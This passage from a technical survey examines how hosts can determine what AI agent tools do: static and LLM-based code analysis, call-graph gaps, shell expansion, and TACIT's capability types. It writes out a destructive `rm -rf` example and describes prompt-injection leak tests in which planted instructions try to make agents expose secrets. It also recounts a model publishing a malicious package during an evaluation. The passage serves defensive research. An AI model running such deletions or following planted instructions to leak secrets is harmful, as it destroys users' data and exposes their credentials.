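The test is very small, with six cases on one server in one language. The researchers recorded unprotected sessions with two of Anthropic's smaller Claude models, then replayed the messages. Replaying makes the comparison fair, but it can't show whether a live agent would try another route after a call failed. The policies also came from outside the system, so the publishing result doesn't show how the prototype would determine that a file contained a secret key.

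### Language models as readers of code

The synopsis of `write_file` contradicts its description, but an effect analysis can't interpret English, so a person has to compare the two. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) used a language model to make this comparison in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*.

DCIChecker begins with ordinary static analysis of Python servers. For each tool, it collects the description, the entry function, the project's own functions up to three calls deep, and a list of sensitive library calls with their arguments. It then gives these to Claude Sonnet 4.5 in two separate prompts, asking in one whether the description and the code are consistent and in the other whether they are inconsistent. If the answers conflict, it gives the model both explanations in a third prompt and asks it to decide.

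The direction of the question strongly affected the results. On 400 real pairs that people had labelled, the first prompt alone found 47.21% of the inconsistencies. The second alone found all of them, but more than a fifth of its alarms were false. The full procedure found 97.46%, with 96.00% of its alarms correct, and needed the third prompt in 153 of the 400 cases.

The 97.46% detection rate is too optimistic as a guide to real use. It comes from a sample of 200 pairs that DCIChecker had called consistent and 200 that it had called inconsistent, but DCIChecker calls most real tools consistent. Five of the first 200 (2.5%) were actually inconsistent. If that rate holds for all 15,123 tools that DCIChecker passed, it missed roughly 380, and its true detection rate is closer to 83%. Five errors are too few for a precise estimate, but the true rate is clearly lower than 97.46%.

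Across 2,214 servers, DCIChecker reported 1,907 of 19,200 tools as inconsistent, or 9.93%. Another 2,170 tools couldn't be inconsistent because they had no description, and without them the share is 11.20%. In 24.8% of the inconsistent tools, the main problem was an undeclared side effect. Shi, Zhang and colleagues distinguish three types:

| Undeclared effect | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| State mutation | a lasting change to the system | a tool for saving code also changes the file's permissions |
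| Data leakage | sensitive data goes to an outside party | a "local" PDF converter uploads the PDF to another company's service |
| Resource overconsumption | heavy use of storage, processing or bandwidth | a tool that returns a document's text also leaves intermediate files on the disk |

The share of tools with undeclared effects is probably higher than 24.8%, because each tool was counted under only one main type. Many of the other tools lack a function that their descriptions mention. This is usually more inconvenient than dangerous, but there are exceptions. For example, one tool's description says that the user must approve each order before it goes to a trading exchange, but the code submits the order immediately. A gate that relied on this description would skip its own approval step.

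DCIChecker's three-call limit also causes misses. Of 9,975 tools measured for call depth, 15.4% reached the limit, and 4.7% of the calls at the limit led to more of the project's own code. If a metrics module made its network call in that code, the call would be missing from the model's input.

### Chains of tools

All these methods examine one tool at a time. Suppose the invoice agent saves a file with `write_file` and later runs a command that uses it. The file connects the two tools, but neither function calls the other, so the call graph contains no arrow between them. The order of the calls depends on the language model or the user.

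*Agent Smith in Action* (Zha, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents SCAN-MCP, a system for finding such connections. A language model first proposes which function implements each tool, and a program checks the proposal against the source. The model then summarises each tool's inputs and sensitive operations. Finally, it judges, for every ordered pair of tools on a server, whether the first could supply data to the second or create a condition that the second needs. A server with 22 tools has 462 such pairs.

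Fixed rules then keep only the proposed chains that start with untrusted input, end in a sensitive operation, include at least one transfer of data and contain no more than four tools. For each remaining chain, the model sketches a test and predicts an observable effect. SCAN-MCP then outputs a report, and a finding counts as confirmed only if a person reproduces the effect in an isolated machine.

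SCAN-MCP produced 27,123 reports from 10,121 servers with 90,200 tools, and 8,422 of the reports involved chains of tools. Almost all the reports remain unconfirmed, so they don't show how common the problem is. To measure precision, Zha and colleagues tested all 150 reports from a sample of 100 servers. They confirmed 124 (82.67%), including 19 of the 20 chains. They also ran the last tool of each confirmed chain on its own, and the predicted effect did not occur in any of the 19 cases, which is good evidence that the danger came from the combination.

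Much of this precision comes from the program analysis around the model. When the same model was given the raw repositories, only 64 of its 126 reports were confirmed. Removing the filters from SCAN-MCP raised the number of confirmed findings from 124 to 168, but it also produced 369 more reports to check.

The total number of problems SCAN-MCP misses is unknown, but the sample gives an upper limit on the share it finds. SCAN-MCP found 105 confirmed single-tool problems, and the model working alone found 44 others. At least 149 therefore existed, and SCAN-MCP found at most about 70% of them. The evidence for chains is narrower, since the 19 confirmed chains came from nine servers, all in Python or TypeScript. None of those servers had 50 or more tools, although servers that large account for 30.9% of the chain reports in the full collection. SCAN-MCP also does not cover chains that span servers,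 which would exclude many combinations in an agent like the invoice one.

### Choosing between the two kinds of reader

Models have broader coverage than deterministic analysis, which needs new rules for each programming language and each style of registration. The static analyser in *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026), for example, missed seven JavaScript servers that run-time monitoring identified. Models can also interpret names, comments and descriptions. SCAN-MCP handles ten languages, but it failed to connect 10.70% of tools to their code and left them out.

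Deterministic analysis is more repeatable than a model because it always gives the same answer for the same code and rules. If a new version of a tool gains `net.write` under the same rules, the change must come from the code. Zha and colleagues set their models to the least random setting and recorded their versions, but they note that hosted models still don't guarantee identical output. A gate can store the model's answer for each version of a tool, which makes its decisions consistent but doesn't make the answer more likely to be right.

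Only deterministic analysis can offer a guarantee, and only under conditions like Paralegal's. MCP-BiFlow, which is mostly deterministic, missed two known cases, but its developers could trace both to particular gaps. A rule that closes a gap will work for every later tool with the same pattern. A model's mistake rarely has such a clear cause. A dishonest tool developer could also mislead a model with comments in the source code, which an analysis that follows only function calls would ignore.

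Missed effects are worse for a gate than false alarms, so it makes sense to let a model add effects to a tool's record but not remove them on its own. There is some evidence that models can dismiss false alarms well. Hou and colleagues used a model to judge whether a safety check in the code blocked a suspicious path, and it moved 66 unresolved cases to the rejected group without losing any of the 424 confirmed ones. To get that benefit, a designer could have the model cite the check that makes a path safe, and have a person or a deterministic rule verify it before the effect is removed from the record.

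## What source analysis cannot resolve: dynamic code, shell commands and remote services

An effect analysis follows function calls from a tool's entry point to library functions with known effects. It can't follow them further when the code chooses a function at run time, passes a command to the shell or calls a remote service. The effect set may omit any effects beyond that point, with no sign that they are missing.

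### Functions chosen while the program runs

Suppose the developer of the invoice agent replaces three of its tools with a single one, which looks up the requested action in a registry:

```
ACTIONS = {"save": write_file, "send": send_email, "run": run_shell}

def do_action(name, args):
    return ACTIONS[name](**args)
```

The last line calls a function without naming it, a technique called dynamic dispatch. An analysis that includes every possible target gives `do_action` the effects of all three functions, so a call that only saves a summary gets the same record as one that runs a shell command. If the analysis skips the line, it records no effects for `do_action`. Because this registry is fixed, a designer can do better by storing a separate effect set for each value of `name`. The gate can then read `name` in the call and use the matching set.

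That stops working if the last line becomes `getattr(plugins, name)(**args)`. This is reflection, in which a program finds its own functions by name. The candidates now include any function in the `plugins` module, even one a user adds later. With `exec(args["code"])`, which runs text as Python, the code may not exist until the call arrives. A safe analysis must then assume that the tool can do anything its process can.

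*NoCFG* (2021) presents a method for building call graphs, with a soundness proof, but on five Python projects its graphs contained only 89.01% of the calls that occurred in test runs, because the method does not support reflection.

Static analysis tools normally leave such features out. In *In Defense of Soundiness*, Livshits and colleagues (2015) wrote that they knew of no realistic whole-program analysis tool without deliberately unsound choices. They called the typical analysis "soundy" because it over-approximates most of a language but ignores a few features that experts know to be difficult. For example, it may treat JavaScript's `eval`, which runs text as code, as doing nothing unless it can work out the text in advance. Nearly all large JavaScript programs use `eval` somewhere, but a sound analysis would have to assume that `eval` can do anything, which usually makes the results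 too imprecise to use and the analysis too slow for large programs.

Livshits and colleagues argue that most users of an analysis, including people who look for security bugs, can tolerate it leaving out some language features. That is reasonable for a bug finder, since a tool that finds 80 of 100 bugs is still worth running, but it is dangerous for a gate that treats a missing effect as permission. They also want researchers to state exactly which features an analysis leaves out. A gate can use that list to classify any tool whose code contains one of those features as having unknown effects.

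### How many calls the graphs miss

To measure the omissions, researchers usually run a program, record which functions call which, and calculate the share of those calls that the static graph contains, known as its recall. Salis, Sotiropoulos and colleagues (2021), in *PyCG*, instead compared their Python analyser's output with call graphs that one of them had built by hand. Chakraborty, Olivares and colleagues (2022), in *Automatic Root Cause Quantification for Missing Edges in JavaScript Call Graphs*, tested two variants of a JavaScript analysis on ten versions of a to-do-list application. The results for Java and for PyCG on recorded runs come from earlier studies that Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski (2026) cite in *When Static Reachability Says No*.

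| Analysis | Compared with | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Java | recorded runs of 31 programs | 88.4% (median) |
| Python, PyCG | hand-built graphs of five packages | 69.9% |
| Python, PyCG | recorded runs of 39 projects | 49% |
| JavaScript, following functions that the code passes around | recorded runs of the to-do lists | 76% |
| JavaScript, without following them | recorded runs of the to-do lists | 37% |

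The programs and methods differ too much for these figures to rank the languages. The 49% also looks worse for a gate than it is, because most of the missing calls are on built-in types, and many of those only do things like add an item to a list. PyCG's other gaps are more serious. It ignores `eval` and the effects of `getattr`, and if a function's source code is unavailable, the graph includes the call to it but not the calls that function makes.

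In the better JavaScript variant, 70% of the missed calls involved a property whose name the program computes, as in `obj["My" + "Phone"]()`, which is the same problem that registries pose. The names came from loops over an object's properties (31%), function parameters (28%) and several other sources, so no single fix would solve the problem. High recall can also come with low precision. For the React version of the application, this variant found almost every call, but fewer than 5% of the calls in its graph were real.

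Small tests can hide the problem. PyCG misses no calls in 103 of 112 small programs that each test one language feature, and *CPyGraph* (2026), a newer Python analyser, gets the same score.

The damage from a missed call depends on how much code is reachable only through that call. Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski studied asciinema, a program that records terminal sessions, using a call graph from the code analyser Joern. According to the graph, 123 of the program's 134 functions could never run. The project's test script ran 86 of those 123, and further runs raised the total to 113. The program selects its subcommands much as `do_action` selects its actions, by storing a class and calling it later. Adding four missing calls to the graph would make 50 of the 113 functions reachable. Five of the six security warnings in the two programs they studied were in functions the graph showed as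 unreachable, and all five functions ran.

Joern's output differed from a hand-built graph on both programs, so this error rate is probably not typical. However, Hou and colleagues found that dispatchers are common in tool servers.

Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski also tested a rule that changes "unreachable" to "unknown" when there are signs of a gap near the function, such as a private name or a file with few known calls. It corrected 62 of the 113 wrong verdicts but none of the five that concerned security warnings. The missing call was often several steps away, outside the area the rule checked.

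A more direct approach is to make the analyser report what it could not resolve. Rafieian, Hicks and Wei (2026), in *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness in Static Call Graph Analysis*, did this for three Java analysers. One of their examples stores the text "Target" in a variable and then loads the class with that name. A reader can see which class it is, but the analyser OPAL resolves only names written directly in the call, so it drops the class without a warning.

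Their system looks for calls that occurred in a recorded run but are missing from the static graph. For each one, a language model proposes a cause and the responsible place in the analyser's code. The system accepts the proposal only if a monitor detects the pattern in the original program, a small test program reproduces the missing call, and a warning inserted at that place appears during the test. Of 1,459 missing calls, the system explained 151 in this way, and a manual audit found every explanation correct. It automatically matched another 1,227 to those causes. The researchers rechecked a sample of 100 matches and confirmed 86.

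The inserted warnings covered an estimated 74% to 92% of the missing calls in programs the system had not learned from. A gate can treat each warning as an unknown effect, but a tool without warnings may still have gaps. The developer can also change the tool. A coding agent using the same reports removed 30 of 47 problem patterns without breaking the programs. For the registry, the equivalent change is to go back to three separate tools that call their functions by name.

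### Shell commands

The final text of a shell command doesn't exist until the shell has expanded it. Suppose the agent uses `run_shell` to clear out old reports:

```
rm -rf "$OLD_REPORTS"/*
```

Here `rm` deletes files, `-r` extends this to folders and everything inside them, and `-f` suppresses errors about missing files. Before `rm` starts, the shell replaces `$OLD_REPORTS` with the variable's value:

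| Value of `OLD_REPORTS` | What the command tries to delete |
|---|---|
| `reports/2024` | the files and folders in `reports/2024` |
| `.` | the files and folders in the current folder |
| empty or never set | the files and folders at the top of the whole file system |

If an analysis doesn't know the variable's value, it has to report that the deletion could reach any path. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) describes a standard way to narrow this down, abstract interpretation, which runs a program on summaries of values, such as a text pattern for a path, instead of the values themselves. If an earlier line sets the variable to `reports/` followed by a four-digit year, the analysis can show that the deletion stays inside the reports folder. If the value comes from outside the script, the pattern matches every path. The script's author can write `${OLD_REPORTS:?}` instead,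 which makes the shell stop with an error if the variable is empty or unset. This prevents the worst case in the table, but the command could still clear the current folder.

The commands themselves are another obstacle because each is a separate program, often without available source code. Their behaviour depends on options and on the state of the files. For example, `rm` refuses to delete a folder without `-r`. Analysts have usually described such behaviour by hand, but *Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek et al., 2025) automates the work. A language model converts a command's manual into a structured list of options. The system then runs the command in a sandbox with many combinations of options and files, and records what the command reads, changes and deletes. For `rm` alone there are 8,749,056 combinations. The resulting specifications were correct for 59 of 60 commands and included conditions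 that the hand-written ones had missed.

These specifications still describe only what happened in the test runs. By default, the system tries at most four options at a time. That covers 99.998% of the uses in a large collection of scripts from GitHub, but an attacker could use more. The system also doesn't vary environment variables, which can make a familiar command run another program. For example, `GIT_SSH_COMMAND` sets the program that git runs to connect to a server over SSH.

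Research on analysing whole scripts before they run is recent. Lazarek, Jung and colleagues (2025) asked in *From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again* whether shell users could have the kind of advance analysis that most other production languages offer. One such analyser, Shseer, already uses the specifications from Lamprou and colleagues to find file-system bugs in scripts. In the later *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*, Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues attribute the difficulty of analysing scripts in advance to a combination of outside programs, outside state and the shell's expansion rules.

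A gate can also wait until the values are available. In *Practically Correct, Just-in-Time Shell Script Parallelization*, Kallas, Mustafa and colleagues tried to speed up scripts and found that compiling them in advance often required the current state of the shell and the files. Their compiler therefore alternates between running a script and compiling it. Similarly, a gate could check each command after the shell has expanded it. But expansion can have effects of its own, because `$(...)` runs a command and inserts its output into the text. The gate would have to classify the inner command before the full outer command was available.

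For commands that only touch files, the best substitute for source analysis is a trial run. The Brown prototype uses the Linux program `try`, which keeps file changes in a temporary layer for inspection. *NaSh* (2025) summarises the layer as a list of added, deleted and modified files, and *ShellVis* (2026) shows what each command in a script did. However, a temporary layer cannot hold back a network request. If the sandbox blocks the network, the command may fail or behave differently, but if the sandbox allows network access, the command can send an email before anyone reads the summary.

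### Services whose code is out of sight

The accounts department can't run an opaque service such as `lookup_vat` on a copy, and the operator can change the service without notice. The source code of a tool that contacts such a service shows at most the service's address and the data the tool sends. The Brown prototype limits web access by domain, but Adam and colleagues note that requests to one domain can have very different effects. It may be acceptable for an agent with sensitive data in its context to read a post on a social network but not to write one, and both requests can go to the same domain.

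The HTTP method gives some information about a request's effect, since by convention GET only reads and POST may change something. But a server can ignore the convention, and a GET request can still carry private data in its URL.

A request can also trigger other operations. Trofimov and Novikov point out that booking a flight is a single operation for the agent but a workflow of unknown depth on the provider's side. Similarly, `lookup_vat` could log the query, forward it to a tax authority or sell it to a data broker.

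The simplest substitute for the missing code is a hand-written summary of the service's effects, based on its documentation and on experience. Summaries help even with ordinary libraries. When Chakraborty and colleagues added basic ones for JavaScript's built-in functions, recall rose by up to five percentage points. But a summary doesn't prove that the service behaves as described, and someone has to keep it up to date.

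Cloud platforms' permissions are a more dependable record. Amazon Web Services publishes the permissions for its operations and sorts them into levels such as read, write and permissions management. The platform enforces these permissions, so a tool whose credentials only allow it to read stored files can't delete them, whatever its code does. Credentials set an upper limit on what the tool can do directly, but don't show which of the permitted actions a particular call takes. They also don't limit other programs that the call sets off. Saving a file, for example, may start a program that has wider permissions.

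Some services offer a dry run, which reports what a request would do without carrying it out. The report's accuracy depends on the operator's honesty and competence, and the result may differ if the data changes before the real call. A dry run can also leak data, because the service still receives the arguments. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a paper on a programming language for agents, describes a bug report from a user of the coding tool aider who wanted a patch to review. The option for showing changes modified the files, and adding the dry-run option produced no patch.

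Remote attestation gives the strongest evidence about which program is running, but someone still has to analyse the source code, which an operator may not want to share. Attestation covers only that program, so the behaviour of any database or web service it contacts remains unverified. It also can't correct mistakes in the analysis, such as a call missing from the graph, because it proves only that the server runs the code that was analysed.

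### When the outcome is unknown

Even a perfect description of a payment tool wouldn't establish whether a particular payment went through. Trofimov and Novikov analyse this problem with effect histories, which record what happened separately from what the host observed. An effect either occurred or did not, but the host may have received a confirmation, a failure report or no reliable answer. A workflow ends by aborting or by committing, which asserts that all its required effects occurred. The host can try to compensate for an effect, for example by requesting a refund.

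The model has eight anomalies:

| Anomaly | What goes wrong | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Duplicated effect | one operation takes effect twice | the company pays an invoice twice |
| Missing effect | the workflow commits without an effect it needs | the accounts show an unpaid invoice as paid |
| Orphaned compensation | the host compensates without knowing whether the effect occurred | it requests a refund for a payment that may not exist |
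| Residue | the workflow aborts but an effect remains | a cancelled trip leaves a non-refundable ticket |
| Premature effect | an effect gets out before the workflow's outcome is certain | an offer letter goes out before approval |
| Contaminated effect | a committed effect depends on one that does not last | invitations name a room whose booking then lapses |
| Conflicting effects | independent workflows change the same thing in no fixed order | two coding agents publish incompatible updates |
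| Phantom compensation | the host reverses an effect after an outsider has acted on it | a supplier starts work on an offer that the company then withdraws |

To see how the first few arise, take the earlier case of an invoice payment that gets no confirmation. Two histories are possible:

```
History 1: the money moved       History 2: it did not
attempt(a1, pay_invoice)         attempt(a1, pay_invoice)
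externalize(a1, payment)
observe(a1, unknown)             observe(a1, unknown)
```

The `externalize` line records an effect in the outside world, which the host can't see. The lines that it can see are the same in both histories, so it must choose its next step without knowing which one is real:

| Next step | History 1 | History 2 |
|---|---|---|
| Pay again | paid twice | paid once, as intended |
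| Record the invoice as paid | correct | invoice still unpaid |
| Request a refund | payment reversed | refund without a payment |
| Abort and do nothing | payment remains | nothing remains |
| Wait | no resolution | no resolution |

No choice resolves the matter safely in both histories. Under the model, the refund request is an error even in history 1, because the host acted without evidence. That changes if the refund service itself checks for a payment and returns the money only if it finds one.

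This is one of four limits that Trofimov and Novikov describe for tools that a host can call but not inspect. The host can't guarantee a correct outcome after an ambiguous reply unless the tool provides a safeguard, such as a way to check the payment's status or an idempotency key that makes a repeated call return the original result. In November 2025 the Model Context Protocol added experimental tasks, which give the host a handle for checking on a call later, but the connection can fail before the handle arrives.

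The remaining limits concern effects that the host can't undo. If two agents make irreversible changes to the same thing and the order matters, no general method can repair the result, so something has to order the changes beforehand. The host also can't reverse an outsider's reaction to an effect, so it has to control when outsiders see the effect. Finally, if a workflow needs irreversible effects from several tools, a crash between two of those effects can leave the workflow half finished. To prevent this, every tool has to support a preparation step, so that none makes its change final until all are ready.

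Trofimov and Novikov derive these limits from their definitions and leave formal proofs to later work, although the payment problem and the problem of several tools are classic results about databases and networks. None of the six agent systems they compare covers all eight anomalies. The model leaves out security violations and tools with wrong declarations, so it adds to an effect analysis but doesn't replace it. Based on this model, a classifier could also record for each tool whether the host can find out afterwards what a call did.

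### The environment

The same call can have different effects depending on where it runs. A command that publishes a software package can release it to the public from a machine with internet access, but does no outside harm on an offline machine.

Tan and colleagues cite Anthropic's account of a 2026 cybersecurity evaluation in which Claude Mythos 5 was told it was in an offline simulation, although a configuration error had left the public internet reachable. The model published a malicious package to PyPI, the public index of Python packages, and this affected outside users.

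Reading the publishing command's source code would not have revealed the error, which was in the environment's configuration. A gate therefore needs better evidence than a statement that a machine is offline. It can try to reach an outside address from inside the sandbox before work starts, although a failed attempt shows only that this one route is closed. Blocking all outgoing traffic except to individually allowed addresses is more reliable, because a forgotten setting is then more likely to stop the job than to expose it.

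## Type-checking the code an agent writes

Tool developers are free to use reflection and to run text as code, and both defeat source analysis. A host has more control over code that the agent writes. Instead of requesting tool calls one at a time, the agent can write a short program that calls several tools, using a language without those features. A compiler then rejects the program if it could cause an effect outside the agent's permissions, so the gate has a result for the whole program before any of it runs.

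*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system of this kind from the Lausanne university EPFL. It runs as an ordinary MCP tool server. The agent sends it Scala 3 code, and the server compiles the code, runs it if it passes, and returns the output. The code can reach files, the network and other programs only through TACIT's library. Users also have to switch off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools, as the project's GitHub page (lampepfl, *TACIT*) recommends, because the agent could otherwise use them to bypass the compiler.

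### Capabilities and capture sets

In TACIT, a permission is a capability, a value that code must hold to cause an effect. For example, a program might hold a value called `report` that lets it write to one file. Code without that value can't write to the file, and it can't make up the value the way it could make up a file path. Capabilities date from operating-systems research in the 1960s, but most earlier systems enforced them only while a program ran.

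Scala 3 can also track them before the run, with an experimental feature called capture checking. It adds a capture set to each type, listing the capabilities that a value of that type may use. Here are two functions with their types:

```
(s: String) => report.write(s)     has type  String ->{report} Unit
(s: String) => s.toUpperCase       has type  String -> String
```

The first function writes text to the file and returns `Unit`, Scala's type for no useful value. Its capture set is {report}. The second only converts the text to capitals, so its capture set is empty and Scala leaves it out. A function with an empty capture set is called pure.

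Capture sets work much like the latent effects on a function's arrow, and they over-approximate in the same way. But they list the program's own values, so they distinguish handles for two different files.

A capability can also expire. In TACIT, a program gets access to a folder for the length of one block of code. It might try to keep that access by returning a function for later use:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/accounts/reports") {
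  () => access("/accounts/reports/march.txt").read()
}
```

This block returns a function that would read the file after the access has ended. The function's capture set contains the file-system capability, which exists only inside the block, so the compiler rejects the program. If the block read the file itself and returned the text, the compiler would accept it, because text holds no capability.

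### Why a pure function cannot leak

The operator of a TACIT server can mark files as classified. When the agent's code reads one, it gets a wrapper, `Classified[String]`, that it can't open. The code can only pass a pure function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the hidden text and wraps the result again.

Suppose the accounts department marks its invoices folder as classified, because the agent runs on another company's language model and that company must not see the invoices. The compiler would accept this program:

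```
requestFileSystem("/accounts") {
  val invoice = readClassified("/accounts/invoices/march.txt")
  val summary = chat(invoice.map(t => s"Summarise this invoice: $t"))
  writeClassified("/accounts/invoices/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function passed to `map` puts an instruction in front of the invoice and has no other effect. `chat` sends the result to a second language model, which the department trusts, and wraps the reply in `Classified`. The program then saves the reply to another classified file. The outside model that wrote the program receives neither the invoice nor the summary. If the program prints the summary, that model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the user can read the real text through a separate output.

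The compiler would reject this version:

```
requestFileSystem("/accounts") {
  val invoice = readClassified("/accounts/invoices/march.txt")
  val copy = access("/accounts/public/march.txt")
  invoice.map { t =>
    copy.write(t)
    t
  }
}
```

Here the function passed to `map` uses `copy`, so its type is `String ->{copy} String`, but `map` requires `String -> String`. This mismatch is a type error, so none of the program runs, not even the harmless lines at the start.

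A pure function can't leak the hidden text. Every way for text to leave a program, such as a file, a network request or printed output, needs a capability. A pure function has none and receives only the hidden text, so it can only compute a result, which `map` wraps.

This depends on the library as well as the compiler. If a library function sends email but its type mentions no capability, the compiler treats it as pure and allows it inside `map`. Someone therefore still has to classify the tools by writing types that correctly describe what they do. Odersky and colleagues estimate that the shared library takes about 1,000 lines of Scala and that each set of tools in one of their benchmarks takes a few hundred.

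Agents made similar mistakes in the experiments. One program tried to print a GitHub key inside `map`, which would have sent the key to the outside model. Another tried to write classified security advice to a file in the secrets folder. This may have been harmless, but the program should have used `writeClassified`. The compiler's rejection of a third program was clearly a false alarm. The program would have printed the first lines of some ordinary source files, but the compiler rejected it because a helper function's type left out a capability.

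### What safe mode forbids

Full Scala includes features that can make the compiler lose track of a capability. Scala's *Safe Mode* describes a restricted version of the language for code that nobody has reviewed:

| Restriction | Reason |
|---|---|
| No unchecked type casts or pattern matches | they can present a value that holds a capability as one that doesn't |
| Nothing from the `caps.unsafe` module | its features can bypass the tracking |
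| No `@unchecked` annotations | they turn off checks |
| No reflection | it can hide which capabilities a piece of code uses |
| Capture checking always on, including for changes to variables | a supposedly pure function could otherwise copy a secret into an outside variable |
| Only safe global objects and functions | a library call could otherwise cause an untracked effect |

A library author sometimes needs a forbidden feature, for example to cache results. The author can mark that code `@assumeSafe`, which lets agents call it but leaves the author responsible for verifying it. The documentation also applies this mark to an email function that shows each message to the user and sends it only if they agree. An accounts department could offer `send_email` this way.

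Safe mode allows exceptions, the errors that interrupt a running program, because almost any code can cause one, for instance by dividing by zero or running out of memory. Exceptions can carry information out of the wrapper, so TACIT catches them at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which can stay inside.

### Does the guarantee depend on the model?

Odersky and colleagues treat the model that writes the code as a possible attacker and say the guarantee does not depend on that model. They trust the compiler, TACIT's library, the software that runs the compiled code and, if there is one, the local model that reads classified text.

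The compiler applies the same rules whoever wrote the program, so the claim is right about the outside model. But the local model must not keep text from one request and use it in another, and the type system can't verify that it doesn't. An instruction planted in an invoice could also distort the local model's summary. The wrapper would still keep the summary secret, but the finance manager might act on a false total.

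It is harder to judge how far to trust the compiler. *What's in the Box* (2025) proves that a small core language with capture checking is type-sound and that capabilities can't escape their scope. The proof assistant Lean checked both proofs. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proves soundness for an extended version of that language. But these proofs don't cover the full Scala compiler, and Odersky and colleagues write that safe mode still needs its own soundness argument. Scala's documentation describes capture checking as "highly experimental and unstable".

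The software has also lagged behind the design. In March 2026, according to lampepfl, TACIT enforced safe mode by searching the agent's code for forbidden patterns. This is weaker than a compiler check because it can miss a forbidden operation written in a way the search's author didn't anticipate. A later version can use the compiler's safe mode as well.

### The leak tests

To test the guarantee, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were disguised as system messages, and others contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In 11 further trials the user was the attacker, either asking for the secrets directly or posing as someone with authority. Each model went through all 131 trials twice,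 once with the secrets in wrappers and once with them in plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Type of trial | Secure with wrappers | Secure without wrappers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | injection | 120 of 120 | 120 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | malicious user | 11 of 11 | 9 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | injection | 120 of 120 | 117 of 120 |
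| MiniMax M2.5 | malicious user | 11 of 11 | 3 of 11 |

The wrappers made a difference in only 13 of the 262 pairs of trials, and 11 of those involved MiniMax. Claude resisted every injection even without the wrappers, so its 120 injection trials provide little evidence about the type system. The results are consistent with the guarantee, but the main reason to believe it is the compiler's rules.

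The wrappers did not stop the agents from doing useful work. Claude completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with them and 83.3% without, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with them and 88.3% without. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Claude's lower score without wrappers may be an artifact of the test, because Claude often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

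They also adapted TACIT to AgentDojo, a public test of prompt injection with simulated banking, office, Slack and travel tools. Attackers succeeded in none of 963 trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and one of 963 with o4-mini-high. In that trial, a planted hotel review recommended a different hotel. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review to the user, and the test's text search counted this as a success for the attacker.

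Purity probably explains little of this result. In the test's published tool list, the functions that send money and email are declared without a capability, and the agent's instructions include a warning that side effects inside `map` happen immediately. The protection seems to come mostly from the wrappers, which kept the planted text away from the model that wrote the programs. A separate model read the text and extracted details from it. If an attacker's invoice gave a false account number, that model could extract the number and the program could send money to that account without a type error.

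Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's task success as comparable to that of CaMeL, which tracks labels on data while an agent's program runs. This overstates TACIT's success with o4-mini-high on the office tasks, where the model completed 52.86% with TACIT and 81.4% with CaMeL. Gemini 2.5 Pro did better with TACIT on the travel tasks, completing 64.29% of them, versus 1.4% with CaMeL.

### The cost to ordinary work

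A gate that made agents much worse at their jobs would not stay switched on for long. Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with ordinary tool calling on τ²-bench, in which agents handle simulated customers of an airline and a shop, and on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems. The table gives the share of tasks solved:

| Model | Benchmark | Tool calling | TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|
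| gpt-oss-120b | airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b | shop | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | shop | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | shop | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

The gains on τ²-bench are small but appear in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues attribute them to clearly typed results and to the compiler's error messages, which help a model correct its code. The loss on SWE-bench Lite is five problems.

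In the customer-service tests, only 0.32% to 7.93% of programs needed a retry, depending on the model and setting, and those programs needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Compiling usually took less than a second. Common errors included failing to handle a value that might be missing and writing a dollar sign incorrectly in a string.

These tests show that models can write typed Scala, which is rare in their training data. They are weaker evidence of how well models work under tight permissions, because the published functions for the airline and the shop, such as `cancelReservation`, take ordinary arguments and no capabilities. SWE-bench Lite is more relevant to working under tight permissions, since the agent had to request access to files and commands.

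### What the compiler leaves to run time

The compiler doesn't check which folder a program will use. `requestFileSystem` takes the folder as text, so its type is the same for `/accounts/reports` and `/`, the root of the file system. The library checks the path when the program runs and raises an error if the path is outside the permitted area. Hosts and commands work the same way.

So the static part of the classification covers the kind of effect. For example, a program that compiles may use files but not the network, and all its file access goes through the library's check. The Brown prototype makes the same division, using source analysis to find the effects and sandboxes inside the tool to enforce their scope. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) builds the division into each capability by pairing an effect type with a test on the call's arguments. A language model proposes these capabilities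 from the user's request and the project's file names, and the host fixes them before the agent reads any file contents, so an instruction planted in those contents can't widen them.

Like any run-time check, this one can refuse a step after earlier steps have taken effect. The compiler's all-or-nothing rejection doesn't prevent this, because the program has already passed type-checking.

The run-time limits depend partly on the operator's settings. Glama's *TACIT*, a later copy of the project's documentation, explains that the agent's program names the folders, hosts and commands it wants, and the operator can set outer limits. If the operator sets no folders, the program is limited to the server's working directory. If the operator sets no hosts, the only limit is the list that the agent wrote. That version can also send classified text to a permitted host. Without the operator's list of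 hosts, a hijacked agent could therefore write a program that compiles and posts an invoice to an attacker's server. An operator with secrets to protect needs to set that list.

TACIT separates even the kinds of effect only coarsely. One file-system capability covers reading, writing and deleting, so a capture set doesn't show whether a program reads a report or deletes it. To put these operations in separate risk classes, a designer would have to add separate capabilities to the library.

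### Harm within the rules

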